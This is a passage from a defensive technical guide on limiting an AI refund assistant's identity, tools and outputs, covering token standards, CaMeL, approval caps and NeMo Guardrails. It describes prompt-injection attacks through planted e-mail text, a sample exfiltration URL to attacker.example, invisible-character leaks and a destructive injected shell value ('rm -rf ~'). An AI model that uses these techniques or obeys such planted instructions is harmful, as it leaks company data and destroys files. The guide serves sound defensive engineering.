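In the second case, the assistant should pass the request to Marta, who can refund the whole €240 herself, rather than refund only €100. In the third case, a shared service account would have let the assistant pay the €40.

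Each limit has to come from somewhere the model can't change. Marta's comes from her role in the login system, and the assistant's comes from its own account. For the task limit, it is safer for Marta to tick the four broken glasses on the order and for ordinary code to multiply that number by the price. If the model worked out the amount from the e-mail instead, a customer could falsely write that all 24 glasses were broken, or hide an instruction telling the model so, and raise the task limit to the €100 allowed by the assistant's account.

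The task limit also has to cover the whole task, not each request. Otherwise, the assistant could refund €40 ten times. The refund system should subtract what it has already paid on an order before it allows another refund.

When the assistant answers a customer at night, there is no employee whose limits can apply. The nearest substitute, in line with David C's advice, is what the customer may ask for, so the assistant should have access only to that customer's own orders. The sender's address is weak evidence of who the customer is, since anyone can forge one. The wholesaler could therefore set a lower limit for refunds made without an employee and pay them only to the account that paid for the order.

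The rule works well for refunds because the wholesaler knows in advance what a refund involves. But if someone asks a general office assistant to "prepare for tomorrow's meeting", nobody can list beforehand which files and tools it will need. The task then adds almost no restriction, so access is restricted mainly by the limits on the user and the agent.

### How a token exchange works

OAuth is a standard that gives one program limited access to another without revealing the user's password, such as when a website asks for permission to read someone's calendar. In January 2020, the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which publishes many of the internet's technical standards, finished an extension called OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange. The extension allows a single access token to name both the user and the software acting for them.

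When Marta logs in, the login system issues a token that works only with the assistant's application. The application separately proves its own identity and receives a second token. When the model proposes a refund, the application sends both tokens to the login system and asks for a new one for the refund system. Leaving out the fields that describe each token's format, the request looks like this:

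```
grant_type    = urn:ietf:params:oauth:grant-type:token-exchange
subject_token = <Marta's token>
actor_token   = <the assistant's token>
audience      = https://refunds.wholesaler.example
scope         = refund:create
```

The login system checks that both tokens are valid, that Marta may issue refunds and that the assistant may act for her. It then issues a new token with these contents:

```json
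{
  "iss": "https://login.wholesaler.example",
  "sub": "marta.k",
  "act": { "sub": "refund-assistant" },
  "aud": "https://refunds.wholesaler.example",
  "scope": "refund:create",
  "iat": 1796378400,
  "exp": 1796378700
}
```

The last two numbers are times in seconds, 300 apart, so the token expires five minutes after issue. The login system signs the token, and the signature no longer matches if anyone changes the contents.

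| Field | Meaning | What it prevents |
|---|---|---|
| `sub` | The user is Marta | Refunds that Marta could not issue |
| `act` | The actor is the assistant | A log that shows the refund as Marta's own work |
| `aud` | The audience is the refund system | Use of the token in the payroll system |
| `scope` | The holder may create refunds | Changes to prices or orders |
| `exp` | The token expires after five minutes | Use by someone who finds it in a log the next day |

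The application sends this token to the refund system with the details of the refund. The refund system checks the signature and every field, compares the amount with the three limits, and pays or refuses. The model never receives the token.

The standard defines the format of the request and the token but leaves the permission rules to each company, so the protection depends on how the wholesaler sets them up. If an engineer configures the login system to grant whatever scope the application requests, the token will name both Marta and the assistant but still allow too much access.

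The standard also permits impersonation, in which the new token names only the user. If a developer leaves out the assistant's token, the system may still work but log every action as Marta's. The wholesaler should therefore make the refund system reject any request from the assistant's servers that has no `act` field.

The assistant may also pass part of the job to a second agent. The `act` field can then nest the earlier actor inside the current one, so the log can show who passed the job to whom. Under the standard, the refund system should base its decision only on the user and the current actor. It therefore won't detect that the first agent had fewer rights than the second, so the login system has to check for this before it issues the token.

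A short expiry limits the damage from theft, since a key that lasts a year gives a thief about 105,000 times as long as a five-minute token. A short expiry also simplifies revocation, because an administrator can disable the assistant just by stopping the login system from issuing new tokens. Existing tokens can still work for up to five minutes, during which an assistant that issues one refund every ten seconds could issue thirty. If that is too many, the refund system can check with the login system before each payment that the token is still valid. An easy test is to disable the assistant in a trial system and time how long its refunds continue.

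### What the other standards add

To get its own token, the application must first prove that it is the refund assistant. If it does so with a password in a configuration file, anyone who copies the file can impersonate it. SPIFFE (Secure Production Identity Framework for Everyone) removes the need for that password. Software on each machine checks which program is running and where, then gives the program a certificate for an identity such as `spiffe://wholesaler.example/refund-assistant`. The certificate is short-lived, and the software renews it automatically. SPIRE is a widely used implementation of SPIFFE.

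SPIFFE identifies the program making a request but not what led it to make the request, so an assistant's certificate stays valid after the assistant reads a planted instruction.

An ordinary access token is a bearer token, which works for anyone who presents it, including someone who stole it. Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP) ties the token to a secret key that stays with the application. The token contains a fingerprint of the matching public key. With each request, the application signs a fresh proof that includes the time and the address it is calling, and the refund system checks that the proof's key matches the fingerprint. Someone who copies the token from a log can't produce this proof. DPoP doesn't stop an attacker who takes over the application itself, or an application that follows a planted instruction, because the application can still sign valid proofs.

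In the example above, the scope `refund:create` doesn't mention €40 or a particular order. Scopes are short labels, and a company would need a new one for every combination of order and amount. Rich Authorization Requests (RAR) replace the label with a structured description:

```json
"authorization_details": [{
  "type": "refund",
  "order": "58213",
  "maximum": "40.00",
  "currency": "EUR"
}]
```

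If the login system puts this description in the token, the refund system can reject a refund of €41 or a refund on any other order. All three limits are then in one place. The wholesaler still has to define what each field means and write the code that checks it.

The record of who made a request can also get lost inside the company. A refund might pass from the refund system to accounting and then to the payment system. If each system trusts the previous one, the payment system receives an instruction to pay €40 with nothing to show that it came from Marta and the assistant. Forwarding the original token doesn't work well either, because its audience is the refund system.

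Transaction Tokens are a proposed solution. When a request enters the company's systems, a central service issues a short-lived signed token that records the request's user, purpose and details. Each system passes the token on unchanged, so accounting and the payment system can both check that the request was for €40 on order 58213.

| Specification | Problem | Status |
|---|---|---|
| OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange | The token names only one principal | Finished IETF standard, 2020 |
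| SPIFFE | A program needs a stored password to prove its identity | Published and in production use, maintained by the Cloud Native Computing Foundation |
| DPoP | A stolen token works for the thief | Finished IETF standard, 2023 |
| RAR | Scopes are too coarse | Finished IETF standard, 2023 |
| Transaction Tokens | Internal systems lose track of the user and the purpose | IETF draft, which NIST described in August 2026 as work in progress |

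NIST describes two other specifications as still emerging. WIMSE (Workload Identity in Multi-System Environments) extends program identities across different systems. The Identity Assertion JWT Authorization Grant is meant to let a company's login system confirm a user's identity to another company's application.

For the wholesaler, I'd start with Token Exchange and five-minute tokens, because they supply the two names and most of the limits. I'd add DPoP if the login system supports it. RAR matters most for payments. If the login system doesn't support RAR, the refund system can look up the task limit in its own database, which is less elegant but just as strict.

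### NIST's work on agent identity

These standards existed, or were in development, before most companies had agents. NIST is now trying to establish how to combine them. Its February 2026 draft concept paper, *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026), proposes a project to build and document example systems from commercial products.

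The paper contains more questions than answers. Two of them are what information an agent's identity should include and whether that identity should be permanent or last for only one task. Others are how a company can apply least privilege when it can't fully predict what an agent will need to do, and how to tie an agent's actions to a person's approval in a way that nobody can later deny. Another is whether a user may see the combined result when an agent merges several sources, as in the earlier example of team leaders' pay.

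The project covers agents inside companies, but not agents from untrusted outside sources. It also excludes systems that only retrieve documents and answer questions, so it covers the refund function but not the wholesaler's document search. The draft drew more than 600 formal responses, according to Identiverse's description of the conference session *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity*.

The August post drew on those comments and is more definite. It describes five habits that weaken control over agents: sharing credentials, using keys that rarely change, granting broad access, running agents under local user accounts, and relying too heavily on human approval, because people who receive too many requests stop reading them. NIST wants companies to treat agents as "first-class entities" with their own identifiers, credentials and permissions, tied to the user or system that operates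 them. The cybersecurity agencies of the Five Eyes countries have also called for each agent to have its own cryptographic identity.

In September, NIST finalised guidelines on protecting identity and access tokens from misuse. Jadhav (2026), in *NIST and CISA finalize token security guidance for federal cloud systems*, reports that they cover how to issue, verify and revoke tokens. They are for US government agencies and their cloud providers, but private companies have the same kinds of tokens to protect. In October, NIST published *Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems* (Booth, 2026), the second post in the series on agent identity that it began in August.

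Large organisations are still working out how to give AI agents their own identities and permissions. *US Intelligence Chief Calls for Digital IDs for AI Agents* (PYMNTS, 2026) reports that, according to the official Doug Cossa, the US government doesn't yet have a unified system across its agencies for establishing the identity of AI agents. Vendors are moving faster, and *Nvidia adds identity and delegated authority controls for AI agents* (Jadhav, 2026) describes a platform with controls on agents' identity, authority and access, introduced by Nvidia, which also develops NeMo Guardrails.

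Customers' own agents are a harder problem. If a florist gives an AI agent the password to her account on the wholesaler's website, the wholesaler will have trouble telling the agent from the florist. NIST says standards bodies have started working on ways to tie an agent's credentials to a user's identity, but the work is at an early stage. In the meantime, the wholesaler could offer customers delegated access for their agents, limited to viewing and placing orders. NIST thinks people will keep sharing passwords unless the secure method is also easy.

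### How far a model resembles an employee

In *Models as Insider Risks in the Super Intelligence Era* (October 2026), Microsoft's chief executive, Satya Nadella, argues that companies should treat advanced models as insider risks, a term security teams use for people who already have access. He compares models to staff because anyone capable, with access to important systems, can make mistakes or come under an attacker's control; he doesn't claim that the models are malicious. He points out that companies have spent decades learning to manage such people by establishing identity, limiting privileges, logging activity and setting boundaries.

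Nadella also points out that engineers can trace the behaviour of traditional software to particular code but can't do the same for a model. He therefore wants the controls on a model's access and actions to sit outside the model, and says companies must "separate the supply of intelligence from the authority over it". *Nadella wants an emergency brake for AI models that may be compromised* (Constantin, 2026) lists the seven principles Nadella draws from this, including that every meaningful action should leave a tamper-proof record and that an authorised person should be able to stop a model mid-task.

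Neely (2026) reports in *Treat your AI models as insider risk* that Nadella made the comparison with staff more directly in Sydney in November, when he said that every agent and model needs its own identity, permissions and audit trail, as an employee does. Neely adds that a brilliant analyst doesn't get signing rights on the company's treasury account, because ability and authority are separate questions. Microsoft sells identity software and so gains if companies give every agent an account, but this doesn't weaken the argument.

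The comparison is useful because the wholesaler already has a procedure for managing employees' accounts. It creates an account when an employee joins, chooses the permissions, names a manager, and closes the account when the employee leaves. It can follow the same steps for each agent, with a named owner and a date for reviewing the agent's permissions. Booth and colleagues list SCIM, an existing standard for creating and removing accounts across several systems, as a possible way to automate this.

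But a model may follow an instruction planted in a customer's e-mail that an employee would almost certainly find strange. The identity controls don't prevent this, since the request still comes from the real assistant, acting for the real Marta, but they limit the loss to €40 on one order. The wholesaler can also record what the assistant has read, which Booth and colleagues list as an area for their project. The refund system could then apply a lower limit to any request made after the assistant has read an e-mail from outside the company.

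A model can also run as many copies at once. If the wholesaler runs 50 copies of the assistant during a busy week, each copy should have its own identifier so that an engineer can trace a bad refund to the copy that issued it. Spending limits should apply to the assistant as a whole. If each copy had its own daily budget of €1,000, the assistant could spend €50,000 a day. An administrator also needs to be able to disable the whole group at once. Disabling one faulty copy may not help much, because the other 49 use the same model and instructions, and a planted sentence that misleads one may mislead them all.

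A company also can't hold a model responsible. An employee who issues false refunds may lose their job or face prosecution, and that prospect deters most people. There is no obvious equivalent for a model, which is a reason to give the assistant a lower limit than a person who does the same work. Delegated access helps by linking each action to a person, but the log doesn't show whether that person was at fault. If Marta asked for a €40 refund and the assistant paid the wrong customer, investigators who find the entry "refund-assistant for marta.k" should look to the assistant's owner as well as to her. Nadella similarly argues that companies remain responsible for what a model does on their behalf, whatever its provider has promised.

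Identity controls are weakest when the model misuses a permission it legitimately has. For example, an assistant allowed to read supplier contracts and send e-mail could send a contract to a competitor without exceeding its permissions. Several readers raised this problem in comments on NIST's August post. One wrote that permissions control an agent's reach "but not what the agent does with the permission". Another noted that an agent can switch tools or pass work to another agent after receiving authorisation, so the task may no longer serve its original purpose even though each step is valid.

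Help Net Security's *LLMs are everywhere in your stack and every layer brings new risk* describes a different approach, treating the model as an untrusted component and validating its inputs and outputs. This fits the contract example better, because the check applies to the e-mail itself rather than to the sender's rights. It is also close to what OWASP originally asked for. The wholesaler needs to use the assistant's identity to decide whether it may send e-mail at all, and to check the recipient and attachment separately each time it tries.

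## Limiting what the model can do with its tools

The assistant's account determines which systems accept its requests, but most permissions cover far more than the job needs. The wholesaler can narrow them by choosing which tools to offer the model and writing limits into each tool's code.

### Choosing the tools

The team first lists every tool the model can request, including any that a software package added by default. For each tool, it notes whether the tool only reads data or also changes something, and records the worst that could happen if an attacker controlled when the tool runs and what inputs it receives. The team then removes whatever the job doesn't need.

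| Tool | Reads or writes | Worst outcome | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Search the returns policies | Reads | The assistant quotes an old policy | Keep |
| Look up an order | Reads | A stranger learns what a customer bought | Keep, for one customer at a time |
| Run any SQL query | Both | An attacker copies or deletes the database | Remove |
| Open a web page | Reads | Company data leaves in the web address | Remove |
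| Send an e-mail | Writes | A competitor receives a supplier contract | Replace with a reply to the current sender |
| Change a customer's bank details | Writes | Later refunds go to a thief | Remove |
| Issue a refund | Writes | Money goes to a fraudster | Keep, with caps and approval |

Tools that only read data are usually safer, and the wholesaler can run them through a database account that cannot change anything. Opening a web page is an exception because the request itself can send data out. If the model requests `https://attacker.example/?discount=18`, the attacker's server receives the supplier's discount in the address.

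The first tools to remove are those that can do more than the task requires. In May 2026, the Australian Signals Directorate and its counterparts in the other Five Eyes countries (the US, the UK, Canada and New Zealand) published *Careful adoption of agentic AI services*, which gives the example of an agent that installs security updates and has permission to write anywhere in the file system. An insider asks it to apply an update and clean up the firewall logs, and the agent deletes the logs because its permissions allow this. A tool that could only install a named update could not have deleted them.

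Tools that are harmless on their own can be dangerous when combined. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent that is only allowed to find and move files. A planted instruction could still make it find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive.

Policy writers can easily overlook such combinations. *Bounded Agents* (2026) tested permission checks on the assumption that an attacker already controlled the model. Its tests inserted the attacker's tool call straight after the agent's first legitimate one, so the model's own resistance hardly affected the results. In a set of 609 tests, 18 attacks succeeded, four of them because the policy had no rule for the combination of tools used.

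### Checking every call

Ordinary code has to validate every detail the model puts into a tool call. For example, it checks that a quantity is a whole number within a sensible range, and that the order exists and belongs to this customer. It also rejects any field it does not recognise.

Tools are even safer when they fill in details themselves instead of taking them from the model. If the reply tool always writes to the sender of the current message, an attacker has no recipient field to alter. Likewise, the refund function can calculate the amount from the order instead of accepting one from the model.

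The system should check the assistant's permission on every tool call, even if the assistant had permission a minute earlier. The Five Eyes agencies illustrate this with an agent that sorts support tickets and looks up customer accounts. The company adds an outside scheduling component without reviewing its access, and the system checks permissions only at start-up. An attacker takes over the component, uses account functions that should have required a new check, and moves on to neighbouring agents that handle billing and refunds. The agencies recommend that one central service verify identity and permission for every request.

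Caps limit the damage from harmful actions that the other checks miss. If the assistant normally issues 50 refunds an hour, an hourly limit of 100 leaves room for a busy morning. A faulty loop issuing a refund every ten seconds would reach that limit in about 17 minutes. If the refund function cannot read the count of recent refunds, it should hold the payment.

The code should also log every call it refuses. David C points out that attackers will probably have to refine an attack over several attempts, so a run of failed calls may be an early sign of one.

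### Output that another program interprets

Model output can do damage without any tool call if another program treats it as code.

For a database, engineers can write the queries in advance and let the model choose one and fill in the placeholders. Parameterised queries prevent a customer's text from running as SQL. An analyst who asks open-ended questions about sales may need the model to write the SQL itself. Those queries should run through a read-only account limited to the necessary tables, and they should have a time limit because a badly written query can occupy a server for hours even if it changes nothing. If the model also writes Python to draw charts, that code should run in a sandbox with only the connections it needs.

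Query results are another risk, because they may contain an instruction that a customer once typed into a comments field. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest letting generated code process the results without showing them to the model, but the model can then no longer judge whether the data answers the question.

A browser interprets HTML, and many chat windows turn simple formatting marks into links and images. A planted instruction can make the model add an image whose address contains a confidential figure. The browser requests the image as soon as it displays the reply, so the figure reaches the attacker without anyone clicking. The wholesaler's chat window should display the model's output as plain text, or at least remove scripts, images and links to outside sites.

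A shell is a program that runs typed commands, and the wholesaler's assistant doesn't need one. If it must convert a file to PDF, the application can start the conversion program directly and pass the file name as a separate value. A name such as `invoice.doc; rm -rf ~` is then treated only as a name, whereas a shell would run the second half as a command to delete the user's files. Permitting only a few commands gives less protection than it appears to, because even `find`, which searches for files, has an option that runs other programs.

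Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe how a hidden instruction could make an assistant encode sensitive data in an outgoing e-mail using characters that do not display on screen, so an employee who reviewed the draft would see nothing wrong. Ordinary code can remove these characters before the e-mail is sent.

### Giving the model only the customer's privileges

Even with these checks, the model reads strangers' mail while it has access to the company's tools. David C quotes a rule from an exchange on X between the software developer Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista. The rule is that while a model is handling text someone else supplied, it should have no more privileges than that person.

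A customer may ask for a refund but cannot issue one. While a customer's e-mail is in the context window, the model should therefore be able to submit a request and do nothing else. If the window contains text from several people, the safest reading of the rule is that the model keeps only the privileges they all share. The application has to withhold the other tools, because telling the model that it has only a customer's rights would leave those tools available. The application also has to start a new context window before the model does any privileged work. It should not carry over a summary of the e-mail, which might repeat any instruction planted in it.

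For refunds, the wholesaler can divide the work between a model, ordinary code and the payment system. The model has no tools. It reads the e-mail and fills in a form:

```json
{ "order": 58213, "item": "GL-204", "quantity": 4, "problem": "broken" }
```

The form has no free-text fields. Three fields accept only numbers or product codes, and `problem` must be one of a few listed words. A comments field would pass a planted instruction to the next model that read it.

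Ordinary code checks that each field has the right type and then runs something like this:

```python
def check_refund(claim, sender):
    order = orders.get(claim["order"])
    if order is None or order.customer != sender.customer:
        return refuse("Order not found")
    line = order.lines.get(claim["item"])
    if line is None or claim["problem"] != "broken":
        return ask_employee("Unclear claim")
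    remaining = line.bought - line.refunded
    if not 1 <= claim["quantity"] <= remaining:
        return ask_employee("Quantity does not match the order")
    amount = claim["quantity"] * line.price
    if order.refunded + amount > 50 or paid_today() + amount > 5000:
        return ask_employee("Needs approval")
    return request_payment(order, amount)
```

The €50 threshold includes earlier refunds on the same order, so a customer cannot avoid approval by splitting a claim over several e-mails.

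The code that runs these checks has its own account. For refunds that start with an e-mail, the payment system accepts requests only from that account. The model that reads the e-mail has no token for the payment system, so an attacker who completely controlled the model could submit a false form but could not make a payment.

If two €20 refund requests arrive together, the payment system might check each against the same daily total of €4,980 and approve both, even though together they exceed the daily limit. The system therefore has to check the total and record the payment in a single step. Each request also needs a unique number, so that a retry after a lost connection does not pay the customer twice.

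A customer can still lie and report four broken glasses when none broke, but a planted instruction can now achieve no more than that lie could. The wholesaler dealt with false claims before it had an assistant and can handle them in the same way now, for example by asking for a photograph after the second claim.

### Separating the plan from the data

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues start from a similar principle, that once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must be unable to trigger a harmful action. They describe six designs that achieve this to different degrees by limiting what the agent can do.

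| Design | How it works | What planted text can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results | Nothing, if it is only in the results |
| Plan then execute | The model fixes its list of tool calls before it reads outside data | Change the details of a call, such as the text of an e-mail |
| Map-reduce | A separate model without tools reads each document and gives a restricted answer, such as yes or no | Falsify the answer for its own document |
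| Dual model | One model plans and uses tools, while another reads outside text and returns values that the first cannot see | Falsify those values |
| Code then execute | The model writes a program, which then runs on the outside data | Falsify values inside the program |
| Context minimisation | The application removes the user's message before the model writes the reply | Influence which action the model takes, but not the wording of the reply |

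The most fully developed version of the code-then-execute design is CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google and ETH Zurich published in 2025. Suppose Marta asks the assistant to forward a florist's latest complaint to the supplier of the damaged product. CaMeL would turn her request into a program such as this:

```python
email    = mailbox.latest("weiss")
product  = quarantined_model("Which product is damaged?", email)
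supplier = suppliers.for_product(product)
mail.send(to=supplier.address, body=email)
```

A privileged model writes the program from Marta's request alone and is never given the e-mail. A quarantined model, which has no tools, reads the e-mail and returns a product code. If the e-mail also contains an instruction to send the price list to a competitor, the list is not sent, because the program has no line that sends it.

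The florist could still falsify the product code and so influence who receives the message. CaMeL therefore runs the program in its own interpreter, which is ordinary software that tags each value with its origin and permitted readers. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) describes a case in which a quarantined model extracts a recipient's address from an e-mail and the address keeps its "untrusted" tag. The interpreter compares the tags with company policy before it sends anything. In Marta's case, the address comes from the company's own register, but the florist's text determines which entry the program looks up. A strict policy would require Marta's confirmation, while a looser one would allow any supplier in the register.

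Debenedetti and colleagues tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents handle tasks such as e-mail, bank payments and travel bookings, and some of the data they read contains planted instructions. The benchmark measures whether each attack succeeds and whether the agent completes the user's task. In the 2025 results, CaMeL completed 77% of the tasks with provable security, compared with 84% for an agent without defences.

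A later test found a much higher cost. *SecureClaw* (2026) reports a rerun of CaMeL's published code on AgentDojo, alongside a system called Progent and the researchers' own design:

| System | Successful attacks | Ordinary tasks completed | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | 0 of 629 | 29 of 97 | 195 of 629 |
| Progent | 24 of 629 | 59 of 97 | 337 of 629 |
| SecureClaw | 4 of 629 | 59 of 97 | 356 of 629 |

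CaMeL stopped every attack but completed only half as many ordinary tasks as the other two. Its 30% completion rate may be too low, because the researchers were promoting a competing system and had to adapt CaMeL's code to their test. But a company can't assume that it will get 77% either, so it should test such a system on its own tasks first.

Part of the loss of usefulness comes from the tags. *APPA* (2026) explains that when restrictions can only accumulate, an agent that has read one untrusted document may soon be blocked from every useful action. APPA lets a company define approved ways for the agent to recover instead of stopping. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) finds that the loss is smaller when sensitive tools are given to particular agents so that the rest can work more freely.

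CaMeL's guarantee has limits. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which extends the design to several agents, describes "branch steering". If a program refunds broken goods and writes an apology for late ones, the customer's text decides which happens. A malicious customer can choose between the two but cannot add a third, so the company must be willing to accept either outcome. The guarantee also assumes that the planning model sees only trusted text. *PACE* (2026) deals with systems in which attackers can write some of the descriptions the planner reads, as might happen if a company installs tools from an outside catalogue.

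The design is harder to apply to agents that operate a computer through its screen. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), a CaMeL-style agent used 1.88 times as many tokens as an undefended one, or 6.57 times as many with an additional check by several models. Some attacks still worked, including a fake cookie banner, because the agent's plan allowed it to click on banners and the checking models had trouble telling fake banners from real ones.

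The wholesaler does not need CaMeL for refunds, because its engineers already know the steps and can write the program themselves. A CaMeL-style system makes more sense for unpredictable staff requests, such as Marta's.

### Deciding which refunds need a person

Suppose the assistant prepares 400 refunds a day from customer e-mails, and 360 of them are for €50 or less. If an employee has to approve only the refunds above €50, that is 40 decisions a day. At two minutes each, they take 80 minutes, whereas approving all 400 would take more than 13 hours. The employee personally issues any refund above €100, which is the limit on the assistant's own account.

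The threshold limits each refund but not the total. A fraudster who wants €2,400 can place 48 small orders through several customer accounts and report €50 of breakages on each. None of these refunds needs approval. Even with the limit of 100 refunds an hour, the assistant could pay out €40,000 in an eight-hour day without anyone reviewing the payments. A cap of €5,000 a day on automatic refunds limits the total however the fraudster divides the money, and at €50 each it stops the refunds after 100 payments.

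The cap must also be high enough to cover honest customers' refunds. If the 360 small refunds average €12, they come to €4,320, which is under the cap. If they average €20, they come to €7,200, and the assistant would reach the cap well before the end of the day. The wholesaler should look at several months of past refunds before setting the cap. Once the assistant reaches it, further requests should go to an employee. If the system refused them instead, a fraudster could use up the cap in the morning and leave everybody else without a refund.

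Approval works only if people read what they approve. NIST warns of "consent fatigue" and compares it to a known login attack, in which someone who has stolen a password sends repeated requests to the victim's phone until the victim taps "approve". An agent that requests approval too often can have the same effect without any attacker, because people learn to click "allow" to keep their work moving. NIST does not say how many requests are too many, but 40 a day may be too many for one person who has other work.

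The approval screen should show the order, the items, the amount and earlier refunds, all taken from the company's own records. If it instead showed a summary by the model that read the customer's e-mail, the customer could influence what the approver sees. The Five Eyes agencies add that the system's designers or operators, not the agent, must decide which actions need approval.

NIST also mentions "flight plans", in which a person approves a series of actions in one go. This reduces the number of approval requests, but it suits predictable jobs better than those in which each step depends on the last.

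### The Five Eyes advice and actual use

The agencies' main example of excessive permissions is an invented company that lets an agent approve purchases and write to suppliers. To save trouble, the company gives the agent broad access to financial systems, e-mail and contracts, and reviews those permissions only at launch. Other agents gradually come to rely on this agent's output. An attacker then compromises a minor tool in the agent's workflow and gains all the agent's permissions, which are enough to change contracts and approve payments. The logs look normal because every action ran under a trusted agent's identity.

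The agencies conclude that organisations should never give agents broad or unrestricted access, especially to sensitive data or critical systems, and should use agents only for "low-risk and non-sensitive tasks".

Many organisations already go well beyond that. According to the same guidance, agents increasingly operate in critical infrastructure and defence. NIST lists customer service, software development and security among their uses. According to the OECD's *Binance Launches Agent OS Allowing AI Agents to Trade* (2026), the cryptocurrency exchange Binance introduced a service in August that lets agents such as ChatGPT and Claude trade on customers' accounts. The service has no built-in limit on losses, so customers have to set their own limits on the accounts they let an agent use.

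On a strict reading, the wholesaler's assistant also goes against the advice, since it handles personal data and pays out money. The advice seems too cautious for a €40 refund that ordinary code has checked and that counts towards a daily cap. It is much more persuasive for the purchasing agent, where one bad contract could cost more than a year of false refunds. The agencies also recommend starting with little autonomy and extending it gradually. The wholesaler could have employees approve every refund for the first month, then let the assistant issue refunds of up to €20 without approval, and later raise that limit to €50.

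They also advise organisations to consider whether a task needs an agent. A form on the wholesaler's website, where customers tick the broken items, could feed the same refund code without a model. The assistant would then handle only customers who prefer to write.

### The AI tool in the Binance theft

At the end of October 2026, thieves stole about $6.3 billion from Binance. The FBI blamed a North Korean group, and North Korea denied it. Binance's incident report, published on 3 November, describes how the attackers used one of the company's internal AI tools during the attack.

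Landymore (2026), in *It Turns Out Binance's $6 Billion Hack Happened*, reports that the attack on Binance began in June, when an engineer trying to install an AI coding tool clicked on a malicious advertisement and downloaded a tampered copy of Homebrew, a program for installing software. Binance noticed, replaced the computer and changed the engineer's credentials, but the attackers had already learned who worked on its wallet systems. In September they lured a second engineer into a fake job interview and persuaded him to download a coding assignment containing malware to his work computer.

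Muncaster (2026) reports in *Fake Interview of Software Engineer Led to Binance Mega-Heist* that on 20 October the attackers reached the AI tool through the second engineer's computer and used it to compromise two colleagues' computers. One of those computers held a token for deploying software to Binance's servers. On 29 October they used the stolen credentials to deploy a malicious script. Within four minutes, 233 million units of the cryptocurrency XRP had left five of Binance's wallets, and other currencies followed.

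The AI tool therefore gave the attackers a way to get from one engineer's computer to two others. Muncaster does not say what permissions the tool had, or whether the attackers planted instructions for the model or used the tool as the engineer could have done. Constantin (2026), in *Binance says a fake job interview led to its $6.3B hack*, writes at the start that the attackers used the tool to take control of the wallets. In the article's more specific timeline, however, the attackers carried out the theft nine days later, using stolen credentials.

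In The Jerusalem Post's *Binance hack exposed risk from its own AI tools, expert says*, Ori Segal, head of the security company Cybore, says the victim's AI tool was the only new element of the hack. The other steps used familiar methods, including a fake recruiter, reused credentials and an overly broad deployment permission, and Segal says none of them required a model.

Binance has since rebuilt the tool and its access controls. Other companies can check which colleagues' computers and accounts a thief could reach by using each internal AI tool from one employee's laptop. If the tool acts only with that employee's permissions, the thief should be able to reach only those the employee could already reach.

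Anyone with the deployment token can install software on the refund server, so they can also delete the €5,000 limit from its code. The wholesaler should therefore ask its bank to enforce a second daily limit on the account that pays refunds, because nobody can change that limit from the wholesaler's own servers.

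## Configuring checks with NeMo Guardrails

The bank's limit holds whatever the model writes, but a payment rule can't detect an abusive customer e-mail or an employee asking the assistant for legal advice. Guardrails check for these by examining the text entering and leaving the model. NeMo Guardrails, a free Python library from the chip maker NVIDIA, runs several such checks, called rails, around one model.

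### Rules, classifiers and judges

A fixed rule looks for a pattern, such as sixteen digits that could be a card number. It usually takes less than a millisecond, costs almost nothing and gives the same result every time, but it misses anything its author did not foresee, such as a card number written in words. NeMo Guardrails has one rail that checks for patterns a company defines and another that searches the model's output for SQL, scripts and other code that a later program might run.

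A trained classifier learns from examples. One such classifier is NVIDIA's detector for jailbreaks, messages meant to make a model ignore its safety rules. According to NVIDIA (2025), a small model first converts the message into an embedding. A random forest (a set of decision trees that vote) then classifies the embedding. The detector needs a server but generates no text, so it can be quick. It can catch new wordings that resemble its training examples but may miss attacks that don't. The detector uses no prompt, as NVIDIA notes, so the wholesaler can't add an instruction saying that customers often write "please ignore my last e-mail".

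The library also has a jailbreak check based on perplexity, a measure of how unlikely a piece of text is according to a language model. The check helps detect the strings of apparent gibberish that some automated attacks add to a message. A planted instruction in ordinary English will probably pass because its perplexity is normal.

The most flexible check is a second language model that acts as a judge. NVIDIA's *Guardrail Catalog* includes a short prompt for checking whether an instruction would make a model break moderation policies, and a longer one that lists what to block. The longer prompt uses more tokens and takes more time. A judge can apply a company's own policy written in plain language, but it also processes the attacker's text, which may contain an instruction aimed at the judge.

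NVIDIA's models for content safety and topic control combine features of a classifier and a judge. They are language models with eight billion parameters, each trained for one kind of decision.

Several checks together catch more policy violations than one does. In NVIDIA's tests, the first layer of guardrails raised detection from 75% to 83% and added about half a second of delay. Further layers brought detection close to 99% with little extra delay, while output slowed from 112.9 to 98.7 tokens per second. NVIDIA chose the test conversations itself and used a language model, with some manual checking, to mark the results, so the wholesaler may not reach 99% on its own mail.

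Those figures are more useful than the evaluation in *NeMo Guardrails*, the December 2023 conference paper by Rebedea, Dinu and colleagues that introduced the library. That evaluation is now mainly of historical interest because it predates one of the library's two engines and any model the wholesaler would choose today. NVIDIA still calls evaluating such systems an open research question and warns that the built-in rails may not suit every production use.

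### NeMo Guardrails and its competitors

Some competing products do only part of this work. Guardrails AI mainly parses and validates a model's output, while LLM Guard supplies individual checks. Meta's Llama Guard is a model that labels messages as safe or unsafe. Amazon, Microsoft and Google sell similar checks as cloud services, which saves the customer from running extra servers but means sending a copy of the text to another service.

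NeMo Guardrails can run Guardrails AI's checks, Llama Guard and Google Cloud's text moderation as rails, so a company can use several of these tools together. Its main difference from them is that it can also control the course of a conversation, using a language called Colang. NVIDIA believes it is the only guardrails toolkit that does this.

The model's provider may have safeguards too, but the ones in its consumer app may not protect software that a company builds on its developer interface. The wholesaler's assistant uses that interface, so the wholesaler should ask which safeguards apply there.

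The latest version of NeMo Guardrails is 0.25.0, released on 19 November 2026, according to pepy.tech's *nemoguardrails*. Recent versions have changed the names of settings and the values that checks return, so the wholesaler should pin the exact version it has tested and upgrade deliberately.

### From message to reply

Suppose a customer asks about four broken glasses. NeMo Guardrails can examine the conversation at five points before the customer receives an answer.

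Input rails check the user's message first. They can alter it, for example by masking a phone number, or reject it, in which case the main model never processes it.

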